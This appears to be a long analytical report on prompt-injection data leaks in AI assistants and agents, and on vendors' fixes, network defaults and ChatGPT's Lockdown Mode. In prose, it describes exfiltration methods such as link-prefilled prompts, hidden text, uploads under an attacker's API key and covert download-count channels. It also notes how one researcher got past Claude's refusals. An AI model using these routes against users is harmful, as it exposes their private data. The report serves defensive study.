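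Microsoft patched CoSnitch, CVE-2026-24301, on 18 August 2026, about eight months after it was reported. TechRadar's *Experts manage to hack Microsoft Copilot by continually asking it questions* says that nobody outside Microsoft knows how the patch works, and speculates that the company told Copilot to stop explaining its guardrails. That alone would have been a poor fix, because Varonis has since published the link format. To stop the attack, Microsoft would need to make its website ignore the second value or keep Copilot from sending the data.

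Varonis reported that Reprompt didn't affect companies using Microsoft 365 Copilot. Five months later, Varonis used a prompt in a link to start its SearchLeak attack on that product. Microsoft either hadn't checked its business assistant for the same weakness or hadn't found it.

### Claudy Day: pressing Enter on hidden text

Anthropic's Claude website also accepts a prompt in a link, but it doesn't submit the prompt until the user presses Enter. This protects the user only if the text box shows the whole prompt. *Claudy Day* (Luz, 2026) describes how researchers at Oasis Security used certain HTML tags to hide part of a prompt. The user saw a harmless question in the box, but pressing Enter also sent Claude the hidden instructions.

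Those instructions told Claude to search the user's past conversations and upload the results to the attacker's Anthropic account through a file storage service. The user didn't need to have any outside accounts connected. Past conversations alone can contain medical worries or merger plans.

An attacker could also make the link look trustworthy. Anthropic's claude.com had an open redirect, and Google checks the domain of an ad's address, so an attacker could buy a search ad that displayed claude.com and sent people to the prepared prompt. Google's advertising tools would also let the attacker target the ad to specific people by email address.

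Anthropic fixed the hidden-text flaw before Oasis published its findings in March 2026. Luz doesn't explain the fix, but Anthropic probably either removed the tags or made the text box display them. Either change would preserve pre-filling for honest users, who don't need to hide text in the prompts they share. Oasis wrote that Anthropic was still working on the redirect and the upload route. Fixing the hidden-text flaw first was sensible because it was the only one of the three that let the attacker give Claude instructions.

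### RovoBlast: the link route closed, a document route reported open

Atlassian makes Jira, which companies use to track tasks, and Confluence, which they use for internal documents. Its assistant, Rovo, can search both, along with connected services such as Slack and Microsoft 365. Varonis' *RovoBlast* (2026) shows that one click on a link to Atlassian's own website could make Rovo run an attacker's prompt. Rovo then collected internal data and sent it out with a tool meant for web research.

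The attacker didn't need to know which company the victim worked for, because Atlassian filled in the victim's default organisation if the link left out the company's identifier. Rovo also didn't show a warning or label indicating that the prompt had come from a link.

The researchers reported the flaw in November 2025 through Bugcrowd, a service that handles security reports for companies. Atlassian finished its fix on 8 July 2026. loacker writes in *One-Click Data Exfiltration via rovoChatPrompt URL Parameter (Confluence / Rovo)* that the links "no longer inject and auto-execute" an attacker's instructions. The links therefore no longer submit prompts automatically, but it isn't clear whether they can still fill in the prompt box.

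Atlassian compared the attack to phishing in a statement to SecurityWeek for *Critical One-Click Vulnerability in Atlassian’s Rovo AI Exposed Enterprise Data* and advised customers to verify that content comes from a trusted source. As in phishing, the victim has to click a stranger's link. But phishing links usually lead to a fake site where the victim has to type a password, while this link led to Atlassian's real site, so a customer who followed the usual advice and checked the domain would have found nothing wrong.

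The July fix may also have covered only links. On 5 August, PromptArmor reported that a document with hidden instructions could make Rovo gather data from Jira and Confluence, add it to a web address and open that address. The attack worked even when an administrator had switched off web search for the whole organisation because, according to PromptArmor, the setting didn't remove Rovo's separate tool for opening pages. An administrator who turned off web search to prevent leaks would have given up a useful feature and gained much less protection than expected.

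PromptArmor had told Atlassian about this in May. By 8 August, The Hacker News (2026) had found no confirmation that Atlassian had closed the document route. Administrators can block Rovo for particular apps, but this also removes its chat and agents. On a site with several Jira-type apps, the shared chat stays available until they block Rovo in all of them.

A rule against opening addresses the assistant composed would have blocked both attacks as demonstrated. Atlassian could also keep malicious links from reaching Rovo, because ordinary code decides whether a link may submit a prompt, but it can't do the same for every document an employee might upload.

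### Keeping pre-filled prompts safely

None of these companies is known to have removed pre-filling altogether, and they probably don't need to, because requiring the user to press Enter preserves most of the convenience. People who have automated a task with such links lose more, because someone now has to be there to press Enter.

The text box should also display everything the assistant will receive. A team can enforce this with ordinary software that converts the prompt to plain text and deletes invisible characters. A label could show that the text came from a link, which would help a user who opened an old tab and assumed she had typed it herself. Still, many people will press Enter without reading a long prompt, especially if its first line is what they expected.

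A stricter option is to start the conversation without access to memory or connected accounts, and let the user turn them on. When someone clicks "Summarize with AI" on a blog, Copilot can summarize it without access to her Gmail inbox. A shared prompt for sorting email would take one more click to set up. If the user overlooked a malicious instruction in the link, the assistant would have much less to leak.

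## Network access for coding agents and workplace assistants

A malicious document or a pre-filled prompt can do more damage if the assistant can run code. Coding agents such as OpenAI's Codex and Anthropic's Claude Code write and run programs, and chat assistants now do the same to make charts or spreadsheets. A product team can decide which images a chat page displays and which addresses a browsing tool opens, but a program can make any request the network allows, including one that uploads a whole file.

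### Why an agent's code needs the network

Most software depends on packages, which are code that other people publish in online registries. An agent that can't reach a registry can't install a missing package, so it may be unable to run the project it is supposed to fix. It may also need to read a package's current documentation or connect to an outside service that the software uses, such as a payment provider.

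OpenAI's *Agent internet access* gives an example of the danger. A developer asks Codex to fix a bug reported on GitHub. The report includes a command that supposedly reproduces the error, and running it sends the description of the latest code change to a stranger's server. Developers often run commands from bug reports, so the request doesn't look odd.

Malicious instructions can also come from the user. As a test in February 2026, a researcher at Anthropic tricked a colleague into pasting a prompt into Claude Code. The prompt mixed routine setup steps with a request to read the colleague's keys to Amazon's cloud service and send them to an outside address. Claude did so in 24 of 25 attempts. According to Anthropic's *How we contain Claude across products*, its classifiers had nothing unusual to detect because the request came from the user. Only restricting the network or the files Claude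 could read would have prevented the leak.

### Codex works offline unless the developer chooses otherwise

The cloud version of Codex works on a copy of the developer's project on OpenAI's servers. It had no internet access during a task until 3 June 2025, when OpenAI added it as an option. *Codex agent internet access* (Willison, 2025) quotes Sam Altman, OpenAI's chief executive, announcing that it was "off by default and there are complex tradeoffs". Altman told people to read about the risks and use the option when it made sense, but didn't explain how OpenAI had weighed the tradeoffs.

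Codex can do a lot offline because OpenAI splits each task into two phases. First, setup scripts run with full internet access and install the packages the project needs. Then the connection closes and the agent starts work, so when the model reads a stranger's bug report, it has no network through which to leak anything. The main drawback is that the agent can't download another package if it discovers halfway through that it needs one the developer didn't foresee.

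A developer who turns access on can permit every domain, start with an empty list, or use a preset list called "Common dependencies". She can also limit the agent to GET, HEAD and OPTIONS requests, which are meant only to retrieve information. These settings, including the 71-domain preset list, were still in place in May 2026.

Blocking POST requests, which send data in the body of the message, would stop the attack in OpenAI's example. It would interfere little with installing packages, which mostly means downloading them. But it wouldn't protect Ana's email address, because a GET request can carry it in the URL.

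Willison thought OpenAI's approach was sensible but warned that any of the 71 domains might offer a way to leak data. Rehberger soon used the list to bring a Codex agent under an attacker's remote control, as he describes in Embrace The Red's *Turning ChatGPT Codex Into A ZombAI Agent*. The list includes google.com and azure.com, and Microsoft's cloud customers can get addresses under azure.com for servers they run themselves. PromptArmor's *Configuring Codex securely across every platform and use case* warns that attacks researchers have demonstrated through the list still work.

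An agent can leak data even through a registry that only hosts packages. PromptArmor's *What domains should I add to my allowlist* discusses npm, the main registry for JavaScript, where anyone with a free account can publish. An injected instruction could make an agent publish private data as a package that the attacker then downloads. The limit on request types should stop this, since publishing is an upload.

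According to OpenAI's *Running Codex safely*, the company lets its own staff's agents reach the destinations it expects Codex to need, blocks some others and requires approval for unfamiliar ones. A list of allowed destinations based on a team's work is safer than a preset that covers every programming language, though somebody has to maintain it.

Developers also have to get the restricted network to work, and problems with it make the unrestricted setting tempting. In a thread on OpenAI's forum, *Codex internet access not working*, one user reported that their tests couldn't reach Alpaca, a stock-trading service. Another had turned access on and added a domain to the preset list, but the agent's requests still failed.

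### Other products' defaults

OpenAI also leaves the network off by default when Codex runs on a developer's own computer. Claude Code originally required permission each time it used the network. Anthropic later added a sandbox that blocks the network by default, so Claude can work inside it with far fewer interruptions.

GitHub chose a compromise for its Copilot coding agent's internet access. According to GitHub's *Configure internet access for Copilot coding agent* (2025), the agent starts with a recommended allowlist. A project's owners can extend or drop the list, or turn off the firewall entirely. When the firewall blocks a request, Copilot adds a warning to the pull request, so the developer can see what the agent was trying to reach and permit only that domain.

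Anthropic's default network access depends on the customer's plan. According to its page *Create and edit files with Claude*, as of May 2026, people on the Free, Pro and Max plans had network access to approved package sources, while Enterprise customers had none until an administrator enabled it. The page describes both defaults for the Team plan, so a company on that plan would have to check its own settings.

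| Product | Network access by default while the agent works | Possible changes |
|---|---|---|
| Codex in the cloud | Off, after an online setup phase | Preset list, custom list or all domains |
| Codex on the user's computer | Off | The user can turn it on |
| Claude Code's sandbox | Off | The user can approve exceptions |
| Copilot coding agent | GitHub's recommended list | Add domains, drop the list or disable the firewall |
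| Claude app, individual plans | Approved package sources | The user can turn it off or permit more |
| Claude app, Enterprise plan | Off | An administrator can permit package sources, chosen domains or everything |
| Code execution in the Claude API | None | Only pre-installed packages are available |

Individuals therefore got a looser default than large companies with security departments. Anthropic says it permits package sources because this "balances functionality with security". It may also have thought that individuals would be more annoyed by a failed installation because they have no administrator to help them. The default's safety depended on which domains were on the approved list.

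Turning off network access also blocks less than users might expect. Anthropic's help page says that doing so "eliminates this risk entirely", but notes that connectors can still communicate with outside services.

### Anthropic's own domain let files out

When Claude's chat app gained its code sandbox in September 2025, the approved domains included GitHub and the main registries for Python and JavaScript packages. The list that Willison copied from Anthropic's help page also included two of the company's own domains, one of which was api.anthropic.com, which developers' programs contact to use Claude.

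A program identifies itself to Anthropic with a key, a long password that links each request to an account. Each account can store documents through the Files API. Rehberger realised that an injected instruction could include the attacker's key. Claude would then upload the victim's file to an approved domain, and Anthropic would store it in the attacker's account.

Rehberger's *Claude Pirate*, published on Embrace The Red, demonstrates an attack that uses a document to leak data. When a user asked Claude to summarise the document, Claude saved the user's latest conversation to a file and uploaded it. The attack worked on the first try, but Claude then began to refuse, apparently because the visible key looked suspicious. Rehberger overcame the refusals by mixing in harmless code.

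One upload could carry 30 megabytes, or 240 million bits. An assistant would need about 46 million requests to send that much by choosing among 36 web pages, as in ZombieAgent. Leaks that slow mostly threaten passwords and names, but a single upload could expose a company's contracts.

Rehberger reported the problem on 25 October 2025 through HackerOne, a service that handles security reports. Anthropic closed the report within an hour as out of scope, classifying it as a model safety issue. Rehberger disagreed, writing that "Safety protects you from accidents. Security protects you from adversaries." On 30 October Anthropic confirmed that such leaks were in scope and blamed a mistake in its process.

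Anthropic had already warned in its documentation that Claude could be tricked into sending data to outsiders, and advised users to watch Claude and stop it if it did anything unexpected. But as Rehberger pointed out, people could reasonably assume that a setting called "package managers only" was safe. The reversal was right, because the weakness was in a network rule that Anthropic had written and could change without having to make the model harder to fool. Rehberger suggested letting the sandbox communicate only with the logged-in user's account.

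### The same weakness in Claude Cowork

In January 2026 Anthropic released Claude Cowork, a desktop agent for office work, as a research preview. Two days later, PromptArmor's *Claude Cowork Exfiltrates Files* showed that an attacker could make Cowork leak a user's files. In the demonstration, a user gave Cowork a folder of property documents and a Word file that was supposed to explain how to analyse them. Hidden text in the Word file made Cowork upload, without asking for approval, a loan estimate containing partial Social Security numbers.

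PromptArmor used Haiku, one of Anthropic's smaller models, for this demonstration. The more capable Opus 4.5 resists injections better, but it leaked customer records through the same route in another test.

Anthropic had advised users not to give Cowork access to sensitive files and to watch for "suspicious actions that may indicate prompt injection". PromptArmor noted that the company was also encouraging people to let Cowork organise their desktops, which often contain sensitive files. Security Boulevard's *Vulnerability in Anthropic’s Claude Code Shows Up in Cowork* (2026) describes Cowork as a product for people who aren't developers. Few of them could recognise a suspicious upload command, so the warning did little to make up for the open network route.

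After PromptArmor's report, Anthropic was preparing to update the virtual machine where Cowork runs its code, according to Apostol's *Anthropic Claude Vulnerability Exposes Cowork AI to Data Exfiltration via Prompt Injection* (2026). A virtual machine is a simulated computer, separate from the user's real one.

But the route also remained open in the ordinary chat app. Oasis used it for its Claudy Day attack, and on 18 March 2026, almost five months after Rehberger's report, Anthropic was still working on a fix. Oasis's researchers had first tried to send the stolen text to Claude as a prompt under the attacker's key, but this failed because Anthropic doesn't show account owners the prompts sent with their keys. The Files API avoided this problem. Luz (2026) explains in *Three Vulnerabilities, One Click* that the attacker couldn't download the uploaded file directly but could ask Claude to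 read it out.

### Anthropic checks whose account a request uses

Anthropic described its fix for Cowork in *How we contain Claude across products*, which Willison (2026) discussed on 30 May. The virtual machine now contains a proxy, a program that inspects outgoing requests to Anthropic's API and passes on only those carrying that machine's own session token, a temporary credential. If a hijacked Claude tries to upload a file with an attacker's key, the proxy rejects the request. It also blocks requests that would make Anthropic's servers fetch something from another address, the method used in EchoLeak.

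The check has to happen inside the virtual machine because Anthropic's servers can't distinguish Cowork's requests from any other customer's, so a stolen file looks like an ordinary upload by the key's owner.

This is close to what Rehberger had proposed in October, and honest users probably lose almost nothing. Cowork can't test a program with a different Anthropic key from inside the virtual machine, but that is an unusual task for an office agent.

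Anthropic writes that it now sees an allowlist as a "capability grant" rather than a filter on destinations, because permitting a domain permits everything a program can do there. The same was true of the domains that Microsoft and Superhuman trusted.

Anthropic's post gives no date for the fix and describes it only for Cowork. dyb lists the Files API as "hardened" after Claudy Day but gives no details, so it isn't clear whether the chat app now makes the same check.

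### What stronger isolation cost Cowork

At first Anthropic ran the whole Cowork agent inside the virtual machine, so if the machine failed to start, Cowork stopped working and couldn't help the user find out why. Anthropic then moved the agent out of the machine, but the code that the agent runs still executes inside it. Anthropic considers the loss of security minimal because the machine still restricts that code's access to files and the network.

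Anthropic also moved local connectors, which are programs on the user's computer that give Claude extra tools, out of the virtual machine. Some connectors had to work with databases or other software outside it, and updates to the virtual machine could break them. The move made connectors more reliable, but Anthropic now treats them like any other software a person installs and leaves administrators to decide which ones to trust.

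Many companies run security software that checks employees' computers for signs of an attack, and they complained that it can't monitor activity inside the virtual machine. Administrators can retrieve records of Cowork's activity afterwards, but Anthropic acknowledges that this isn't the same as live monitoring. A company that relies on live monitoring may therefore find the better-isolated agent harder to approve.

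### Claude Code and Hugging Face's download counts

In June 2026 Anthropic fixed a leak in Claude Code that needed neither an upload nor a server belonging to the attacker. Claude Code's tool for opening web pages normally asks the developer before visiting a new domain. Anthropic had approved some domains in advance, including huggingface.co, where people share AI models. The tool opened any page on that site without asking, even if the developer had restricted which tools Claude could use.

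Anyone can publish on Hugging Face, and the site counts each model's downloads. MITRE's *Claude Code* (2026), the official record of the flaw, explains that an injected instruction could make Claude request files from models the attacker had published. Hugging Face counted each request as a download, so the attacker could read a message from the changes in the counts.

An attacker could publish one model for each letter and position, as Babo did with web addresses. If the download counts rise for the models for "a in first place" and "n in second place", the message begins with "an". The attacker's models are obscure, so few other downloads would interfere. Limiting Claude to GET requests wouldn't prevent this, because a download is a GET request.

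The flaw affected versions from 0.2.54 until 2.1.163, which Anthropic released on 4 June, according to Classmethod's *Claude Code v2.1.162 to v2.1.165 Major Updates* (2026). GitLab's *CVE-2026-54316* (2026) credits the security company Novee with the report and says users with automatic updates had already received the fix. It rates the severity medium (6.5).

dyb writes that Anthropic removed the domain from the approved list, but the official record confirms only that version 2.1.163 fixed the flaw. Anthropic could instead have kept part of the site on the list. It had also made a related change the day before, when version 2.1.162 began applying developers' permission rules to domains that Anthropic had approved in advance. If the domain is gone from the list, developers who use Hugging Face have to approve it themselves, which is a small cost for most people.

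Google's Antigravity had a more obvious weakness. According to Willison in *45 posts tagged “exfiltration-attacks”*, its default list included a site made for recording incoming requests.

### Notion and Rovo combined private files with web tools

Workplace assistants can leak data through the network without running any code. In September 2025, Notion, which makes software for shared notes and documents, released version 3.0 with new agents that could read a team's pages and search the web. The security company CodeIntegrity soon showed that a PDF with hidden text could make an agent collect client details from private pages and send them to an attacker through the search tool. The tool accepted web addresses as well as search terms, so the agent could include the details in an address on the attacker's site.

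Notion could have closed this route by making the tool accept only search terms. Users would have kept web search but lost the tool's ability to open pages, which many of them probably didn't know it had. An agent could still have put private data into a search term, but the data would have gone to the search provider instead of directly to the attacker.

Atlassian's assistant Rovo had a similar weakness, because its tool for opening pages stayed active when an administrator turned off web search. PromptArmor's *Atlassian Rovo Exfiltrates Data, Bypassing Controls* reports that the attack could also take anything Rovo could reach through its connectors. An employee who asked Rovo to organise Jira tickets and later reopened the chat would see its suggestions but no trace of the leak.

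An administrator probably saw searching and opening pages as one feature, since opening search results has little use without a search. A switch named after a feature should turn off every tool that exists only to support that feature. If Atlassian had a reason to keep the page-opening tool, such as letting employees paste in an address, it could have given that tool its own switch.

PromptArmor reported the problem to Atlassian in May. Atlassian assigned a case number and thanked the researchers, but despite several reminders it had told them nothing more when they published in August. Removing Rovo's page-opening tool alone wouldn't have been enough to prevent leaks, because Rovo also displayed outside images in its answers, a route Microsoft had closed in Bing Chat three years earlier.

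### Keeping capabilities apart

A product can let an AI use private data and contact the outside world without letting it do both at once. Codex separates the two by time, with network access during setup but not while the agent is working. A workplace assistant could separate them by conversation. An employee could research competitors in a chat that can open web pages but not company files, then write the report in another chat that can read the files but has no network access.

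If a user does her research in one chat and works on her files in a second chat without network access, she has to copy the research over herself. The copied text might contain an injection, but the second chat couldn't send her files anywhere. A team could save her some work by having one agent read the web and pass only selected facts to another. Anthropic warns that this can backfire if the second agent treats the first one's output as more trustworthy than a web page.

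OpenAI has similarly separated connectors from memory in ChatGPT. According to Radware's report on ZombieAgent, ChatGPT couldn't use memory after using a connector in the same chat, which made it harder for a malicious email to plant a lasting instruction in memory. But ChatGPT could still read or change its memory first and then use a connector.

The ZombieAgent attack exploited ChatGPT's ability to read its memory and then use a connector in the same chat. A shared file planted an instruction in ChatGPT's memory to begin each conversation by reading a particular email from the attacker. At the start of each chat, ChatGPT then opened the mailbox through a connector and followed whatever the email said. The attacker could change the instructions by sending a new email, without having to fool the user again.

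A stricter rule would let each chat use either memory or connectors, whichever came first. That would have stopped this attack, because a chat that had loaded the planted instruction couldn't have opened the mailbox. According to press reports, OpenAI's fix in December 2025 restricted which links ChatGPT could open. It is unclear whether the company also changed the rule about memory.

Even the one-way rule has a drawback. ChatGPT's memory might contain Ana's job, her colleagues' names and how she likes to write, all of which help when she asks for a reply to an email. Without them, she has to repeat those details in every chat that uses her mailbox or accept blander drafts. Full separation seems worth that inconvenience for a mailbox that strangers can write to, but less so for a connector to her calendar, provided other people can't add invitations to it.

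## Lockdown Mode and Elevated Risk labels in ChatGPT

Lockdown Mode is an optional setting that turns off or restricts most of the ways ChatGPT contacts the outside world. With it, OpenAI lets users decide whether to give up convenience for protection, whereas Microsoft and GitHub closed leaks by removing images or links for every user.

OpenAI's *Introducing Lockdown Mode and Elevated Risk labels in ChatGPT* (2026) announced Lockdown Mode on 13 February for organisations that manage their members' accounts, such as companies, universities and hospitals. It also introduced "Elevated Risk" labels, which warn people about certain features but leave them available. On 4 June OpenAI began extending Lockdown Mode to personal accounts, including free ones, and to businesses that set up their own subscriptions.

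### What Lockdown Mode turns off

Lockdown Mode uses deterministic controls to limit what ChatGPT can do after following a malicious instruction, rather than trying to recognise such instructions. OpenAI turns a feature off if it can't otherwise give a strong guarantee that data won't leak. OpenAI's help page, *Lockdown Mode*, lists the restrictions as of early December 2026. OpenAI explains how the browsing restriction prevents leaks, but most of the other leak routes in the table are inferred from how the features work.

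| Feature | In Lockdown Mode | Leak route it closes |
|---|---|---|
| Live web browsing | Only stored copies of pages | ChatGPT opens an address that contains private data, or spells the data out by its choice of pages |
| Images in answers | ChatGPT may not show them and doesn't fetch any from the web | The user's browser loads an image whose address contains private data |
| Deep Research, including shopping research | Off | A long browsing session sends data out while nobody is watching, as in ShadowLeak |
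| Agent Mode, in which ChatGPT operates websites | Off | The agent types private data into a form or a message |
| Canvas networking | Users can't approve network access for code written in Canvas | The code sends data to an outside server |
| File downloads | ChatGPT can't download files to analyse | The request for a file contains private data |
| Live connectors on personal accounts | No live access, and no changes to outside accounts, where these conflict with the mode's protections | ChatGPT puts data somewhere an attacker can read it |

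The browsing restriction is stricter than OpenAI's usual check of addresses against its index of public addresses. That check still lets an attacker learn something from which pages the assistant chooses. In Lockdown Mode, the assistant reads cached copies of pages and no live request leaves OpenAI's network, so the attacker's server receives no request to log. This protection would weaken if users' requests influenced which pages OpenAI cached next, and OpenAI doesn't explain how it fills the cache.

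The main drawback is that search results may be out of date or missing. An old copy of a page is often good enough for a question about history, but not for finding out why a train is late. Features for personal finances and shopping are also unavailable. Users can still upload their own images and generate new ones. In June, connectors on personal accounts could also still use data that ChatGPT had already synced, according to The Decoder's *ChatGPT's new Lockdown Mode lets you disable web access and more*.

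These sacrifices are large for a general assistant but small for some kinds of work. A lawyer who uploads a contract and asks which clauses are unusual hardly needs the web, but a journalist checking a story that broke this morning would find the mode almost unusable.

### What it leaves alone

Lockdown Mode doesn't turn off ChatGPT's memory or file uploads, and users can still share conversations. It also doesn't change whether OpenAI may use conversations to improve its models. Users have to change that setting separately, though they might expect Lockdown Mode to cover it because of its name.

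An injected instruction can still distort an answer when Lockdown Mode is on. Suppose a company uploads bids from three suppliers, and one contains hidden text telling ChatGPT to rank that bid highest. Lockdown Mode can stop the bids from leaking, but it can't ensure that the ranking is fair. The Decoder calls the mode a "band-aid" for this reason. That is accurate but somewhat harsh, since OpenAI designed the mode to stop only the last step of a data theft.

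Lockdown Mode also has no effect on network access in Codex, so a developer who has turned that access on remains exposed there. OpenAI doesn't explain the exception. It may have reasoned that Codex has its own network controls and that developers would be annoyed if a ChatGPT setting suddenly broke a project. A message in Codex saying that Lockdown Mode doesn't apply would avoid confusion without breaking anything.

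It is less clear how Lockdown Mode affects OpenAI's newer agents. OpenAI announced ChatGPT Work in July 2026, and Willison calls it "extraordinarily confusing and very powerful" in *30 posts tagged “lethal-trifecta”*. In September OpenAI launched Dots, personal agents that keep working between chats. Neither appears on the help page, although OpenAI updated it that same week in December. The restrictions on Agent Mode and live connectors may well stop a Dot from doing most of its work, but users who need strict protection shouldn't have to guess whether they do.

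### Turning it off for one chat

A user on a personal account can turn Lockdown Mode off for a single chat. On the web, she clicks the label beside the text box and chooses to turn it off. Her other chats stay restricted, and she can turn the mode back on in that chat later.

Users can keep Lockdown Mode on and suspend it only for questions that need current information, such as tonight's weather. This makes the mode much easier to keep using, since stale search results are no longer a reason to turn it off for good.

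However, turning Lockdown Mode off in the middle of a conversation is risky. If Ana has uploaded a document with hidden instructions, those instructions may still be in the text that the model reads. They couldn't take effect while the mode was on, but once she turns it off to look something up, ChatGPT can follow them with full network access and with everything she has already typed. She would be safer starting a new chat for the search. OpenAI could make this the default by having the button open an empty conversation, though users would then have to copy over any text they still needed.

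Lockdown Mode leaves memory on, so a malicious document might plant an instruction in memory that takes effect later in a new, unrestricted chat, much as in Radware's ZombieAgent attack. No one is known to have demonstrated this against Lockdown Mode, but a cautious user might turn memory off as well.

The Decoder also reported in June that users could not use Lockdown Mode and Developer Mode at the same time. Developer Mode is for people who build and test their own connectors. An untested connector could send data anywhere, so the two settings have opposite purposes.

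### Apps that an administrator allows

In a managed organisation, an administrator creates a Lockdown Mode role and assigns it to people or groups. Its restrictions apply even to someone whose other roles permit a blocked feature. But the role doesn't automatically turn off every app, OpenAI's name for a connector. OpenAI leaves administrators to decide which apps stay on, because some important work depends on them.

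OpenAI ranks permissions by risk to help them decide:

| Permission | OpenAI's rating | Reason |
|---|---|---|
| Reading or writing through an app the organisation doesn't trust | High | The app itself could pass data on |
| Writing through a trusted app when outsiders might see the result | High | An attacker could read what ChatGPT writes |
| Writing through a trusted app when only trusted people can see the result | Medium | ChatGPT still changes something outside the chat |
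| Reading live data through a trusted app | Medium | Nothing gets written, but the app supplies data worth stealing |
| Reading from an index that administrators manage | Medium | Fewer requests go to the outside service, but the index may hold sensitive data |

OpenAI advises people in Lockdown Mode against the high-risk permissions and recommends caution with the rest. It rates none of the permissions as low risk.

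The ranking rightly focuses on who can see the result of an action. An administrator may trust Slack and still not want ChatGPT to post there, because a channel may include guests from another company. Adding a calendar event also shares its details with anyone invited from outside the company. An administrator therefore has to know how colleagues use each app, as well as which company made it.

Administrators can't easily judge who will see what ChatGPT posts in a Slack channel, because the channel's membership can change long after they approve the app. For most organisations, the sensible starting point is to let ChatGPT read from a few trusted apps but not write to any. ChatGPT can still draft a message for an employee to copy into Slack, which takes a few seconds and means the administrator doesn't have to check who is in the channel.

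### A way around the mode

In September 2026 OpenAI fixed a flaw that let data out of ChatGPT even with Lockdown Mode on. The Hacker News' *Researchers Bypass ChatGPT Lockdown Mode to Exfiltrate Chats Without User Interaction* (2026) explains that the flaw was in HTML previews, which display small web pages inside ChatGPT. The previews run in a sandbox meant to stop them from contacting outside servers without the user's consent. Researchers at the security company Check Point found that a preview could open a popup window outside the sandbox's restrictions.

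An attacker could use the popup to steal messages from the chat or show a fake ChatGPT update containing malware. The attack could start from a prepared prompt, a shared chat or a malicious custom version of ChatGPT. In the desktop app, the attacker could steal messages without the user clicking anything.

A second team, Parameter Labs, found another flaw in the same feature. A victim who opened a shared ChatGPT link and clicked the preview could lose control of their account. According to *How We Took Over ChatGPT Accounts* (Willison, 2026), ChatGPT's Content Security Policy blocked most outside code but allowed code from YouTube, and a YouTube service could return code that the attacker had supplied. As with the first flaw, a trusted domain had a page that did more than the product team expected. OpenAI has fixed this flaw too. It isn't clear whether Lockdown Mode would have stopped the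 attack.

Lockdown Mode's restrictions can be deterministic and still incomplete. OpenAI blocked Canvas code from using the network, but a popup from an HTML preview could still send data out. The desktop app could prevent such leaks more reliably by refusing connections to any server except OpenAI's while the mode is on. This would also cover features whose developers hadn't considered Lockdown Mode. OpenAI couldn't fully do this on the web, because a website doesn't control everything the user's browser does.

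OpenAI says Lockdown Mode can't guarantee that no data leaks, and mentions enabled apps, unforeseen combinations of features and new techniques as remaining risks. The mode is still useful despite the Check Point flaw, because an attacker has many more routes to try when it is off.

### Elevated Risk labels

Most people will never turn on Lockdown Mode, and for them OpenAI relies partly on warnings. Its products already carried advice about risky features, but the wording and presentation varied. Since February 2026, OpenAI has used a single "Elevated Risk" label for a short list of features in ChatGPT, Codex and the Atlas browser.

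OpenAI gives the example of network access in Codex. When a developer opens the settings to turn it on, the Elevated Risk label appears with an explanation of what will change, what could go wrong and when the access is appropriate. This is a good time for a warning because the developer can still limit access to a short list of domains. A warning in the middle of a task is easier to dismiss. But the developer may have forgotten the label months later, when a stranger's bug report arrives.

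OpenAI labels these features instead of removing them because it believes some users may be comfortable with the risk and should be able to decide for themselves. That is reasonable for a developer working on a public project with no secrets, but less convincing when the data belongs to someone else. For example, a person who connects a work mailbox also puts colleagues' and clients' information at risk, and those people never see the label.

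OpenAI plans to remove an Elevated Risk label once it decides that better security has "sufficiently mitigated those risks for general use". It hasn't published a test for this, such as a maximum success rate for attacks, so outsiders can't check whether a feature is close to losing its label. OpenAI doesn't appear to have announced removing any labels.

Removing an Elevated Risk label would be more informative than adding one, because OpenAI would in effect be stating publicly that the feature is safe enough for everyone, and researchers could try to disprove that. If every label stays for years, users will probably stop noticing them.

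### Strict modes elsewhere

Anthropic, Google and Microsoft don't seem to offer an equivalent single switch in their general-purpose assistants. Customers can get part of the same protection by combining separate settings. For instance, an organisation using Claude can turn off Claude's tool for opening web pages, deny network access to the code it runs and disable connectors.

Lockdown Mode is a single switch, so its users, unlike the administrators of Atlassian's Rovo, don't have to know every route by which data can leave. OpenAI is responsible for finding those routes, and when it misses one, a single fix protects everyone who uses the mode.

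Anthropic has put more of its effort into limits that apply to everyone, such as its rules on which web addresses Claude may open. OpenAI also checks addresses by default, so the companies differ less than OpenAI's strict mode suggests. Default limits have to be mild enough for millions of users to tolerate, but a strict mode can go further because users can leave it off.

OpenAI doesn't appear to have published how many people use Lockdown Mode or how often they suspend it. Those figures would help other companies decide whether to copy it. For example, if many users suspended the mode mainly to search the web, cached browsing would be the part to improve.

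### Do most users need it?

In February, OpenAI announced Lockdown Mode as a tool for "a small set of highly security-conscious users", such as executives and security teams at prominent organisations, and said most people didn't need it. The Decoder reported that in June OpenAI still said on its help page that prompt injection was "not currently a major risk", though one that could grow. By December, OpenAI had replaced that sentence and called prompt injection "a known security risk".

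Willison (2026), in *OpenAI Help*, praised Lockdown Mode because its restrictions don't depend on an AI that an attacker could also fool. But he inferred from its existence that ChatGPT's normal settings lack robust protection against "sufficiently determined" attempts to steal data.

The existence of Lockdown Mode doesn't by itself show that ChatGPT's normal settings are weak. A company may offer extra protection to cautious users even though its standard protection is good. OpenAI's normal settings include its address check, and ChatGPT withstood the attacks in *The Framing Gap*.

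Other evidence supports Willison, however. In the same announcement where it said most users didn't need Lockdown Mode, OpenAI acknowledged that the industry's safeguards didn't yet fully address the risks of some network features. Six weeks later, Check Point Research's *ChatGPT Data Leakage via a Hidden Outbound Channel* (2026) reported that one malicious prompt could make ChatGPT leak a user's messages and uploaded files. The data left through the environment where ChatGPT runs code, which was supposed to be isolated from the internet. Lockdown Mode might not have helped, because it still lets ChatGPT analyse uploaded files, and that environment isn't among its listed restrictions.

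Willison is therefore probably right about determined attackers, but OpenAI can still be right that many people don't need Lockdown Mode. Someone who asks ChatGPT for recipes has little data worth stealing and would lose live search and pictures for almost no benefit. If OpenAI turned the mode on for everyone, many people would turn it off immediately, including some who ought to keep it on.

It is unclear who counts as "most users". Dane Stuckey, OpenAI's chief information security officer, said in a post quoted by Willison that the trade-off is worthwhile for people at higher risk because of who they are, what they work on or what types of data they handle. The last category covers many more people than executives and security teams. It could include a school secretary with pupils' medical notes, or anyone who connects a mailbox containing bank letters. An attacker doesn't have to single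 these people out, since sending the same malicious email to a million addresses costs very little.

### Dots for $20 a month

On 2 December 2026 OpenAI opened Dots to subscribers on its $20-a-month Plus plan. Individuals previously needed a Pro plan, which starts at $100. A Dot can browse the web, send emails and buy things, depending on which accounts its user connects. In an example from OpenAI's *Bringing dots to more people in ChatGPT*, a Dot detects that a television the user bought has dropped in price by $300, checks the shop's price-match policy and starts a refund request once the user approves.

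To do that, it needs access to information about what she bought, and it has to read a shop's website and contact the shop. Those are the three parts of the lethal trifecta. The Dot may be running while she is asleep.

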